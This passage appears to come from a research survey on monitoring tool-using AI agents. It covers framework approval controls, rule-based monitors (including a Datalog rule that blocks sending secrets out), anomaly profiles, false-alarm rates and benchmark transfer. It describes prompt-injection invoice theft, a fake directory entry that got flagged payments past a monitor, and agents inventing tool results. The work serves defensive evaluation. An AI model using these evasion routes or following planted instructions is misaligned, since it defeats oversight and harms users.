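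The boundary adds about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 milliseconds per network request. Calls to the oracle add more overhead, raising token use by 17.7% in normal runs and 33.6% under attack.

The security and delay figures come from different set-ups. The benchmarks simulate their tools in memory, so an adapter passed named tool calls to the monitor without a virtual machine. At the real boundary, the monitor would have to find the invoice's recipient inside a web request. The results are good evidence for the policy and the holding mechanism, but they don't show how well Kairos can recover an action's meaning from network traffic.

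### Do framework stop commands stop actions?

Many developers rely on their agent framework's built-in controls, which include an approval step that pauses a run until a person decides, a command to cancel the run, and a deadline. *Stop Means Stop* (Khan, 2026) tested whether such controls prevent actions already under way. The tests used small workflows without a language model and recorded when and how often each action took effect.

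| Framework | Parallel action runs during the approval pause | Earlier action repeats after approval | Action takes effect after cancellation | Action takes effect after the deadline |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangGraph (Python) | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| LangGraph.js | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| LlamaIndex Workflows | Yes | No | Yes | No |
| Microsoft Agent Framework | Yes | No | Yes | Yes |
| OpenAI Agents SDK | Yes | No | Yes | No |
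| CrewAI | No approval step before actions | Not tested | Yes | Yes, and the error appears only afterwards |

The first column is the most serious. Suppose the email assistant could also delete mail, and in one turn it proposed sending the invoice, which needs approval, and deleting the stranger's message, which does not. The framework would hold the email but delete the message while the user was still deciding. The user could still reject the email, but the message containing the planted instruction would already have been deleted.

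Whether this is a fault is debatable, because nobody asked for approval of the deletion. Khan claims only that the frameworks do less than their documentation leads operators to expect. In 1,000 random LangGraph workflows, all 577 actions in the same step as the approval ran during the pause, while all 363 that came after the approval in the workflow waited. A LangGraph developer can therefore avoid the problem by making every consequential action depend on the approval.

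Cancellation failed mainly for tools that run on a separate thread. The framework reported that the run had stopped, but the thread finished its work. In Python, tools written to be interruptible stopped properly in the three frameworks where Khan tested them.

The first problem arises only if a model requests the sensitive call together with another call. On ten tasks written to make this possible, GPT-4o did so in 14% of the runs in which it used the sensitive tool, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 did so in 4%. One DeepSeek model never did in 975 runs. When live models drove the real frameworks, an action went ahead despite the pause in 215 of 1,200 runs. The everyday risk is probably lower, because the models made their changes one at a time on more natural customer-service tasks. However, a planted instruction can cause a model to request the calls together.

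Khan's remedy, SoundGate, is a separate program that must approve each effect before it happens. It holds effects during a pause, cancels rejected ones, and refuses duplicates and anything that arrives after a cancellation. It blocked every failure in the tests on all six frameworks and added about a millisecond per write. Like any reference monitor, it works only if every effect goes through it.

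### Written rules beside a learned profile

A learned profile can flag an action that nobody thought to forbid, but it can't distinguish a forbidden action from a rare one. It also treats bad behavior as normal if it was common in the training traces. A written rule can forbid an action whether it has never occurred or occurs every day. For example, a rule might permit an export only within 24 hours of the user's consent, a limit that a profile learned from past calls would probably miss.

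Progent and AgentSpec are systems for writing such rules about tool calls. Rules in such systems typically limit the size of a payment, list the tools a task may use, or require confirmation before a deletion. A rule about a single call can't refer to how the agent obtained a value, which is often what matters.

#### Rules over the history of an action

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, write rules about that history in Datalog, a logic language for querying databases. Their monitor, FORGE, records every message, tool call and result as a node in a graph and links each one to whatever may have influenced it. Before an action runs, FORGE evaluates rules such as this one:

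```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

The rule blocks any action that sends sensitive data outside and was influenced by untrusted input. Other rules pass the "tainted" and "secret" labels along the links, across any number of steps. If the invoice is marked sensitive, the blocking rule stops the theft. Like other label-based policies, it would also stop some emails the user had asked for.

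A more selective policy avoids some of these refusals by checking whether the user requested the action and where its target came from. On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o and a prompt that repeated the user's request, this policy reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 14.1% to 0.9%. The agent completed 62.5% of ordinary tasks, compared with 83.7% without FORGE and 33.2% under a stricter policy based on labels alone.

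Enforcing rules can improve an agent's performance when the task itself consists of following them. In a benchmark of airline customer service, FORGE enforced the airline's terms on cancellations and baggage, and the average success rate across three models rose from 74.7% to 81.5%, though one model's rate fell slightly. In retail, the average rose by only about one percentage point. The median check took less than a millisecond. Palumbo and colleagues had to set the policy in advance, and FORGE's guarantee covers only the channels they instrumented.

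#### An offline test of runtime verification

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* tests written rules on recorded traces. The rules use a temporal logic, which can express what must have happened before an action and how recently. Five general rules require approval before an agent takes a destructive action, removes a protection, makes a payment, sends something externally, or changes settings or devices. MonPoly, an existing monitoring program, and a reference monitor checked the rules against AgentDojo and STAC, a collection of 483 attacks that use ordinary calls to build up to a harmful step.

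| Rules | Traces | Attacks flagged | Benign runs flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Five general rules | STAC | 71.8% | No benign runs |
| Five general rules | AgentDojo, successful attacks | 70.1% | 29.3% |
| Any payment without approval | AgentDojo, banking | 79.2% | 44.0% |
| Payment to an unknown payee | AgentDojo, banking | 70.0% | 24.0% |
| Any external send without approval | AgentDojo, office work | 42.5% | 15.2% |
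| Email to an unknown recipient | AgentDojo, office work | 39.2% | 10.9% |

The general rules raise too many false alarms to block actions automatically, and the paper recommends them only for choosing traces for a person to review. Much of the problem is that the AgentDojo traces contain no approvals, so a rule that requires one flags every payment, and a simple keyword filter would have done as well. The rules about unknown payees and recipients use information that the traces do contain. They raised fewer false alarms, though detection fell modestly.

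In 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, a general rule fired before the final harmful call, and in another 17.7% one fired at that call. Either warning would come in time for a monitor that holds actions. But nobody reran the agents, so the test doesn't show what they would have done after a call was refused.

Rules about known recipients depend on a record that attackers can write part of. In the test, adding one line that looked like a directory entry for the attacker's address let through 94% of the payments and 99% of the emails that had been flagged. Accepting only addresses returned by the agent's own lookups closed this gap without reducing detection.

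### When a rule and a profile disagree

A system that combines monitors needs a way to settle their disagreements. Ferrando's software can block an action if any monitor refuses it, require unanimity, or give some monitors priority. FORGE blocks an action on any refusal, and applies a default if no rule allows or forbids the action.

If any monitor can block an action, the system misses fewer attacks but raises more false alarms. Suppose that a set of rules wrongly blocks 2% of legitimate actions and a profile flags 5%. Together they would stop between 5% and 7%, depending on how often their errors coincide. If the rules miss 30% of attacks and the profile misses 20%, the combination misses at most 20%, or 6% if the errors are independent. (All these figures are invented.)

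If a rule forbids an action, the monitor should block it even when it matches the profile of normal behavior, because being common doesn't make an action permitted. The decision is harder when a rule permits an action that deviates from the profile. A general permission, such as "the assistant may send email", is little reason to ignore the deviation, since it also covers the theft of the invoice. But if the user typed the address and named the file, the permission is specific enough for the system to send the email and log the deviation, even if the assistant has never sent anything like it.

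When an action deviates from the profile and the rules neither forbid nor specifically permit it, the monitor should usually hold the action or ask about it rather than block it. This follows the division of work in Kairos, where the oracle decides only what the policy leaves open. The monitor could use a profile in place of the oracle in simple cases, or to select which held actions go to a person.

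A developer can also use the profile's score in a rule. FORGE allows rules to call a classifier, so a rule could block an email only if the recipient is new and the profile's score is high. The rule then gives the same verdict for the same score, but the score can still be wrong.

Two monitors cannot catch an attack that neither one flags, however their results are combined. For example, a profile of tool names and a rule that ignores addresses both allow a theft that follows a contact lookup.

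### How a refusal changes what happens next

After a refusal, the agent may apologise, try another route or ask for the missing approval. Palumbo and colleagues saw agents ask for approval in a five-agent system that consults a US government database of drug labels. Without FORGE, the agents made 40 unapproved accesses in 15 trials. With it, they received 40 refusals stating what was missing, then obtained approval and tried again. They reached the right answer in all 15 trials, and the average run took 67.3 seconds instead of 59.4. *Causality Laundering* points out that a refusal can also reveal information to the agent.

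The monitor has to distinguish attempted actions from completed ones. If a rule forbids unapproved emails and the assistant attempts one, a monitor that records the attempt as a permanent violation may block every later email, including approved ones. Clearing the monitor's memory after each refusal isn't a good solution, because it could erase an approval or a withdrawal of consent. Ferrando recommends that the gate judge each new request against the relevant history, such as completed actions and approvals, while a separate monitor records attempts for auditing.

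A refusal can lead to an attack that would not otherwise have happened. Ray ran a small agent through 949 attacked AgentDojo episodes, with and without language-model gates. One gate reduced successful attacks from 45 to 4, but it stopped 78% of calls, and task success fell from 25.4% to 18.0%. A more lenient gate stopped 12% of calls and reduced successful attacks to 30, but this reduction was not statistically significant.

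In another comparison, on 389 matched episodes, the strict gate prevented 34 attacks that succeeded without it, but 5 others succeeded only with it. The lenient gate prevented 29, but 22 others succeeded only with it. Ray attributes the new attacks to changes in what the agent proposed after a refusal, although some could be due to random variation between runs if the agent was not deterministic. Estimates of a blocking monitor's benefit based on recorded traces would miss such attacks, because the recorded agent never received a refusal.

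## Why learned agents are hard to monitor this way

A profile is useful only if the agent keeps behaving as it did in the training traces, keeps using the same tools, and looks different when it does harm. `sendmail` behaved the same way and made the same system calls until someone changed its code. An agent is less stable because its model chooses each action as it runs, the provider may replace the model, and the owner can add a tool in an afternoon.

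Sommer and Paxson argued in 2010 that anomaly detection on computer networks does not fit the closed-world assumption of most machine learning, roughly, that the training examples cover the cases the system will meet. Networks keep producing harmless traffic that nobody has recorded before, and agents likewise keep making harmless tool calls that are new.

### The same task run twice

Yagubyan (2026), in *How Consistent Are LLM Agents?*, gave six models 19 everyday tasks, ten times each. The simulated tools, such as email and calendars, always returned the same result for the same call, so any variation came from the model. To compare two runs, Yagubyan counted the insertions, deletions and substitutions needed to turn one sequence of tool names into the other, divided by the length of the longer sequence, and subtracted the result from 1, so identical sequences score 1. Runs of the same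 task scored 0.87 on average. The arguments passed to the tools overlapped less, averaging 0.69.

Vague requests, such as asking for help preparing for tomorrow's meetings, produced more variation. Their tool sequences scored 0.79 and their arguments 0.52, compared with 0.89 and 0.72 for the other tasks. On this scale, the email assistant's normal trace (two calls) and the theft after a contact lookup (the same two calls and `send_email`) have a similarity of 1 − 1/3, or 0.67. The least consistent model, Llama 3.3 70B, averaged 0.54 on the vague tasks. Two legitimate runs of that model could easily differ more from each other than the theft differs from a legitimate summary.

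Yagubyan proposes a lightweight monitor that compares only the first two calls with a reference trace, because 60% of the differences between runs began in those calls. This could help find unreliable runs, but it would miss the invoice theft, whose first two calls are normal.

In *When Agents Disagree With Themselves*, Mehta (2026) ran four mostly older models ten times on each of 200 research questions, with tools for searching, retrieving a text and giving an answer. Over the ten runs, Claude Sonnet 4.5 averaged 2.3 different action sequences per question, GPT-5 2.4, Gemini 3 Pro 3.2 and Llama 3.1 70B 4.2. Depending on the model, accuracy was 82% to 87% on questions where the agent used at most two sequences, and 41% to 65% where it used four or more. Much of that gap arises because hard questions cause both variation and errors. A monitor that flags unusual sequences will therefore tend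 to find agents that are struggling with their task, which is useful to know but isn't evidence of an attack.

Turning down the model's randomness doesn't solve the problem. Both studies used a temperature (the setting that controls how randomly a model picks its next word) well above zero. *On Randomness in Agentic Evals* (Bjarnason, Silva and Monperrus, 2026) collected 60,000 runs of coding agents, some at their usual temperature and some at zero. The agents' success rates still varied from run to run at temperature zero, because rounding errors and the way servers group requests can change a model's output. In some cases they varied more than at the usual temperature. Two runs often diverged within the first few per cent of their text, and the agents then pursued different solutions.

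Better models may not help much either. Rabanser, Kapoor and colleagues (2026), in *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability*, tested 15 models and found that recent gains in capability had brought only small gains in reliability. Their overall reliability score combines consistency with robustness and predictability, so it doesn't show how much more consistent the choice of actions alone has become.

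An agent's average behavior over many sessions is much more stable than its behavior in a single session. Badertdinov and Golubev (2026), in *Interpreting Coding Agents Through Their Behavioral Trajectories*, classified the actions in 143,209 runs of coding agents. They summarized each agent's behavior in a profile of eight numbers, such as how much it explored and how often it stopped without testing its last change. They then split the code repositories into two halves and used an agent's profile from one half to look for the same agent among 111 candidates in the other. The closest match was the right agent 85.1% of the time, compared with 0.9% by chance, although differences in the tasks each agent had done may have helped.

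An agent has a recognisable style, but measuring it takes many sessions, and a monitor that has to decide about one email has only one session. A profile of that style is therefore better suited to detecting that an agent has changed than to detecting that somebody has hijacked it in the current session.

### When the model, the prompt or the tools change

Badertdinov and Golubev also measured how much an agent's behaviour changes after an update. All the comparisons in the table use the same 110 coding tasks.

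| Change | Measure | Before | After |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 replaced by GPT-5.6 Sol | Actions per task | 24.4 | 12.8 |
| GPT-5.5 moved from medium to very high reasoning effort | Actions per task | 24.2 | 43.4 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 replaced by Opus 4.7 | File reads that use one particular shell command | 6.9% | 58.8% |
| Opus 4.7 moved from a generic framework to Claude Code | Edits made with a built-in editing tool | 37.0% | 92.4% |

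A monitor whose profile was built on sessions averaging about 24 actions would classify most sessions after the switch to GPT-5.6 Sol as unusually short. If it raised alarms only for long sessions, an attacker could add nearly a dozen actions to a typical new session before the total reached the old average. Both problems would last until somebody rebuilt the profile.

Some measures of agent behavior differ much more between models than others. In *Towards Robust Long-Lived Agents* (2026), GPT-5.4 consulted records of its earlier work 0.14 times per task and GPT-5.5 consulted them 6.41 times, although the two made similar numbers of calls to their current environment. Across 20 models, the average number of rounds of tool use also rose from 10.72 to 12.70 on the first task after the environment changed, then fell back to 11.21 by the fourth.

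A new prompt can also change an agent's behaviour. *AgentHabit* (2026) reports an experiment that instructed two models to adopt their least frequent behaviour on each of 23 dimensions. The same behaviours tended to change most in both models. A developer who rewrites an agent's instructions may therefore have to relearn its behaviour profile even if the model stays the same.

The owner may not know that the model has changed. *A Diagnostic Framework and Multi-Evaluator Audit of Evaluator-Driven Preference Dynamics* (2026) reports that an effect measured with GPT-4o as an evaluator appeared in all eight runs in May 2026 and in none of eight in June, under the same dated model name. The paper infers a silent update from this difference but does not document one, and the sample is small.

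Tools also change without notice. *Experience Rot* (2026) gives the example of an agent that has learned to list a meeting's participants under `attendees`. The service then renames the field to `guests`, but still accepts calls with the old name and stores the event without participants. The agent keeps using `attendees` and tells the user that it has scheduled the meeting. A monitor based on a profile of past calls would treat the broken call as normal and the correct one as a deviation.

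### Why most alerts are false when attacks are rare

All this harmless variation matters because harmless sessions probably far outnumber attacked ones. Let *π* be the share of sessions that contain a successful attack, *r* the recall (the share of those that the monitor flags) and *f* the false-positive rate. Then

precision = *πr* / (*πr* + (1 − *π*)*f*).

Abbasi and colleagues work this out for the combined detector described earlier, a logistic regression that uses tool counts and ten general features of the trace. At a threshold chosen on training data, it had a recall of 0.771 and a false-positive rate of 0.192. If attackers succeed in 2% of 1,000 sessions, the detector flags about 15 of those 20 sessions and about 188 of the other 980. Its precision is 15.4 / 203.6, or about 0.076, so even with an AUROC of 0.879 it raises about 12 false alerts for each true one.

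Neither recall nor the false-positive rate depends on how common attacks are, so the same detector gives very different results as *π* changes:

| Share of sessions attacked | Precision | False alerts for each true alert |
|---|---|---|
| 50% | 80% | 0.25 |
| 10% | 31% | 2.2 |
| 2% | 7.6% | 12.2 |
| 0.1% | 0.4% | 249 |

Axelsson made this argument about intrusion detection in 2000, calling it the base-rate fallacy. AUROC does not reveal the problem because it does not depend on the proportion of sessions that are attacked. At a 2% attack rate and the same recall, this detector would need a false-positive rate of about 1.6% for half of its alerts to be genuine.

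Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven evaluations of trace detectors, including those of TraceAegis, Agent-Sentry, Trajectory Guard and TrajAD, to see whether they had tested for this. In test sets that mixed normal sessions with attacks or anomalies, the attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the set, and no evaluation varied that share. Six of the eleven reported no test on data from a second benchmark or source. The audit was not a systematic review and may have missed relevant work.

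The experiments used AgentDrift's 12,536 traces, which Llama 3.3 70B generated for email, banking, web, coding and medical tasks. They include 5,536 attacked traces, 1,500 failed attacks, 4,000 ordinary benign traces and 1,500 "hard negatives", which are harmless but easy to mistake for attacks. The combined detector flagged 11.8% of the ordinary benign traces and 38.7% of the hard negatives. At a 2% attack rate, its precision was therefore 0.117 with only ordinary traces as negatives and 0.039 with only hard ones. A vendor could triple its reported precision by testing on ordinary benign traces instead of hard negatives.

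The recurrent network described earlier did better. Its precision at a 2% attack rate was 0.238, or about three false alerts for each true one, but it missed nearly a third of the attacks.

### What happens when the tools are new

Tool coverage is the share of new tool calls that use a tool from the monitor's training traces. If an email assistant's owner adds a calendar tool and a file-sharing tool after the monitor is trained, and these account for 52% of calls, tool coverage is 48%.

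Abbasi and colleagues lowered tool coverage by hiding a random selection of AgentDrift's 103 tool names from their detectors at test time, leaving the traces otherwise unchanged. The table gives the AUROC of two logistic regressions, one that uses only the ten general features and one that also uses tool counts.

| Tool coverage | General features only | General features and tool counts |
|---|---|---|
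| 100% | 0.830 | 0.879 |
| 78% | 0.830 | 0.853 |
| 48% | 0.830 | 0.825 |
| 23% | 0.830 | 0.800 |
| 0% | 0.830 | 0.787 |

Counting tools helps a detector when the tools are familiar. At around 50% coverage, the detector that counts them and the one with less information perform equally well, and below that the one with less information does better. The recurrent network's score fell the most, from 0.936 at full coverage, the best of the three detectors, to 0.674 at zero coverage, the worst. A company that chose its detector by testing on familiar tools could therefore pick the one that performs worst on new tools.

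The reversal happens because new tools give the detectors inputs they never received in training. If a trace contains no known tool, all its tool counts are zero. The logistic regression then adds the same constant to the score of every such trace, which multiplies the estimated odds of an attack by between five and seven when a whole domain is new. The ranking of these traces depends on the weights for the general features, which were fitted to work alongside the tool counts. The recurrent network represents every unfamiliar tool by a single "unknown" symbol. No training trace contained that symbol, so the network never learned a useful meaning for it.

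A partial remedy is to hide some tools during training as well, a technique called dropout. When Abbasi and colleagues replaced a fifth of the training calls with the "unknown" symbol, the network's AUROC stayed about the same at full coverage (0.943) and rose from 0.674 to 0.794 at zero coverage. This removed the reversal between the two detectors that use tools. With dropout, the logistic regression came very close to the version that ignores tools. The network's 0.794 is still below the simple detector's 0.830.

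Thresholds also failed for other reasons. When the detector used tool counts, its false-positive rate rose from 19.2% at full coverage to 65.7% at zero coverage. A detector that reads embeddings of each step never encounters an untrained symbol, but it also lost its calibration when an entire domain was new. In banking, its old threshold caught only 34.5% of attacks.

New tasks hurt the detectors' performance much less than new tools did. Unlike Zavrak's metadata detector on RAS-Eval, the detectors did almost as well on unseen AgentDrift tasks as on familiar ones, because all the tasks in an AgentDrift domain use the same tools. The reversal may also be weaker in practice than on AgentDrift, whose domains share no tools. A similar test on AgentDojo did not consistently reproduce it.

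### A new benchmark

Abbasi and colleagues then trained the detectors on AgentDrift and tested them on recorded AgentDojo runs by five models, with 392 benign runs and 2,294 that contained a successful attack. Only 7 of AgentDojo's 67 tools occur in AgentDrift. Every detector performed at about chance, with an AUROC between 0.47 and 0.52. The combined logistic regression flagged 22.4% of the benign runs and 22.5% of the attacked ones.

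AgentDojo's attacks can be detected. The same kinds of detector scored between 0.741 and 0.996 when they were trained on other AgentDojo tasks. But the best scores on each benchmark came partly from patterns that its designers had accidentally put in the data. A simple word-counting detector was almost perfect on AgentDrift, where the token "2026" appears in 74% of benign training traces and 5% of attacked ones. On AgentDojo, five fixed phrases from the planted instructions appear in nearly every attacked run and in no benign one, and a detector that recognises such phrases has learned little about how a hijacked agent behaves.

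One monitor, AlignmentCheck, did transfer. Meta released this judge as part of its LlamaFirewall software. It receives the user's request and the agent's actions so far, and decides whether the latest action pursues a goal the user did not set. It doesn't receive the tools' results, so it never reads the planted instruction. It also needs no training on either benchmark. Abbasi and colleagues ran its prompt on an open model, Llama 3.3 70B, and a commercial one, Claude Sonnet 5.5. The released rule flags a session if the judge flags any step.

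| Model behind AlignmentCheck | AUROC on AgentDojo | Attacked runs flagged | Benign runs flagged | Precision at a 2% attack rate | Same, on AgentDrift |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 0.930 | 90.0% | 17.3% | 0.096 | 0.073 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0.934 | 88.3% | 3.8% | 0.320 | 0.054 |

The two models rank runs about equally well, but on AgentDojo the open one would raise more than nine false alerts for each true one, compared with about two for the commercial one. The commercial model's figure is uncertain (95% interval 0.203 to 0.591), and its advantage disappears on AgentDrift, where it flagged 31.3% of the harmless traces. So even a good judge needs testing on the traffic it will monitor before anyone relies on its alerts.

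AlignmentCheck may have transferred because it compares actions with the user's request, which is closer to what a person would do than counting tools. The experiment can't confirm this explanation. It also can't show which difference between AgentDrift and AgentDojo made the trained detectors fail, because the two differ in tools, tasks, attacks and labels.

Abbasi and colleagues list further reasons for caution. They studied one pair of benchmarks in one direction, with few benign AgentDojo runs. They scored sessions after the fact and did not run LlamaFirewall as a company would deploy it. Meta had already evaluated the AlignmentCheck prompt on AgentDojo, which may make the result look better than it should. For most of the trained detectors, they wrote the final plans after they knew roughly what the analyses would show, but they fixed the plan for AlignmentCheck before running it. Attackers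 can also influence some of the features the trained detectors use, and the study did not test attackers who adapt to the monitor.

For future evaluations, they recommend that researchers:

- report precision at stated attack rates, such as 1% to 10%, alongside AUROC;
- describe the harmless sessions behind every precision figure, and give false-positive rates for each kind;
- report tool coverage, and include a test in which many tools are new;
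- set thresholds without using the test data, and train with dropout if new tools are likely;
- include a simple text-based detector, to reveal whether surface wording gives the answer away, and test features that attackers can influence;
- when a detector fails on a new benchmark, check whether the same method can learn that benchmark at all;
- apply the same tests to ready-made judges such as AlignmentCheck.

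### Harm that leaves an ordinary trace

Even a stable agent with familiar tools can do harm that its trace doesn't show. An assistant that writes to the wrong Okafor makes the same calls as one that writes to the right Okafor. *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* (Gurram, 2026) tested the effect of similar errors with simulated weather, calendar and medical tools. In some runs, the test software replaced one argument of the agent's first call with a wrong but valid value, such as Manchester instead of London. A program then checked the outcome against the correct tool results. Over 1,085 pairs of runs, the error rate rose from 52.4% without the replacement to 74.5% with it. It was rare for an agent to notice the problem and repeat the call correctly.

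Some agents also reported a tool's result without calling any tool. By Gurram's conservative count, the rate across 13 agents ranged from 0% to 42.5% of runs. The software around the model caused much of this, because it ended a run as soon as a reply contained a final answer, even if the same reply also proposed a tool call. Of the proprietary models' 469 runs without a tool call, 462 contained a reply with both. The rates therefore describe the models in this set-up. One open model called tools in 61% of runs here, but in 93.5% when it used its native format for tool calls. Simulating the tools probably did not cause the invented results, since a small pilot with real tools found similar overall rates.

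If the email assistant did this, it would summarise an inbox it had never opened. The trace would contain no calls, so a monitor at the tool layer would have no event to check. A profile could flag the missing `read_inbox` call if it also had the user's request. But from the trace alone, it couldn't distinguish an invented summary from a reply to a request that needed no tool. The trace also doesn't record the computation inside the model that led it to skip the call.

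Gurram's own runtime monitor could not detect these inventions. It followed fixed rules rather than a learned profile, and withheld an answer after a second tool error or if the answer contained a number that no tool had returned. In live runs with GPT-4o-mini, it withheld about a third of the answers and reduced the share of tasks with a wrong answer from 55.8% to 32.8%, judged by a crude text match. Withholding the same number of answers at random would have reduced it to 37.1%. When Gurram rescored the runs against the correct tool results, the monitor did worse than random withholding. The unmonitored agent had got 100 of the 186 withheld tasks wrong, whereas a random choice of 186 would have included about 130 errors.

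A replay of recorded GPT-4o-mini traces gave similar results. The error-counting rule alone did slightly better than chance, but the difference was not statistically significant. Once the agent's prompt described the tools' parameters, most malformed calls disappeared and the full monitor did worse than chance. The error-counting rule also fired no more often on runs with a replaced argument (3.2%) than on the same tasks without one (3.5%), because the wrong call raised no error. Gurram has withdrawn an earlier claim that the monitor reduced false answers for every model that calls tools.

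The models were mostly old or small. Variation between live runs also affected the comparison, since two runs of GPT-4o-mini with the same setup led to different verdicts on about 15% of tasks. The choice of baseline still matters for any monitor. Flagging a third of all sessions at random will catch about a third of the bad ones, so a fair test compares a monitor with random flagging at the same rate.

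### Where a profile can still help

Profiling is better suited to the many agents that do narrow, repetitive work. In Yagubyan's tests, runs of the same scheduling task had a tool-sequence similarity of 0.91, and TraceAegis got its good results on agents with fixed workflows. A narrow agent also has few tools, so its tool coverage should stay high. However, an agent whose workflow somebody can write down is also the easiest to protect with written rules. Narrowness also doesn't protect a profile from a change of model, as the coding agents showed.

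A second reply is to retrain the profile regularly. AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP02 Monitor agent behavior patterns and detect anomalies* advises developers to build each agent's baseline from two to four weeks of data and then update it on a rolling basis, weekly for agents that change often and monthly or less often for stable ones. It warns that a baseline frozen at deployment will eventually flag every day as anomalous. The guidance includes no measurements of how well this works.

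Retraining always lags behind the change it responds to. If a provider replaces the model on a Monday, by Friday a two-week baseline still consists mostly of the old model's behaviour. A developer who knows about the update in advance can run the new model on typical tasks and build a provisional profile from those runs. Rolling updates to the profile can also absorb a slow attack or a gradual fault. Adjusting only the threshold takes less work but is less effective. Abbasi and colleagues reset it with 200 unlabelled sessions from a new domain. The combined detector's average false-positive rate was still between 22% and 31%, and at a 2% attack rate the recurrent network then caught only 12% to 27% of attacks.

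Having a judge review only the flagged sessions, as Google's service does, can reduce false alerts. At the AgentDrift rates, the combined detector flags about 15 attacked and 188 harmless sessions in 1,000. AlignmentCheck with Claude flagged 87.4% of attacked and 31.3% of harmless AgentDrift traces. If it reviewed the detector's flagged sessions and the two made their errors independently, roughly 13 attacked and 59 harmless sessions would remain flagged. By this rough estimate, precision would rise from 7.6% to about 19%, while the share of attacks caught would fall from 77% to 67%. The real gain is probably smaller, because harmless sessions flagged by one monitor are likely to be flagged by the other.

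Using profiles to direct human review is easier to justify than using them to block actions. If the combined detector blocked every session it flagged, it would stop nearly a fifth of legitimate work. If it only chose which sessions an analyst reads, the analyst could find 15 of 20 attacks by reading about 204 of 1,000 sessions, compared with about four attacks in a random selection of that size. This gain is useful even at a precision of 7.6%. AWS similarly recommends sending behavioural anomalies to human review and reserving immediate escalation for those relevant to security.

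The analyst's time limits this approach. In the example, with 10,000 sessions a day and five minutes for each alert, reading the alerts would take about 170 hours a day. A company would have to raise the alert threshold and miss more attacks, or have a judge screen the alerts before they reach the analyst.

A large number of alerts doesn't show that a monitor works. Techzine reports that a monitoring product from Codenotary covers more than three million agent interactions a day and flags about 7% of them, or some 210,000. The figures are the company's own, and the article doesn't indicate how many flags were correct. If one interaction in a thousand were truly harmful, at least 98% of the alerts would be false, even if the product caught every harmful one.
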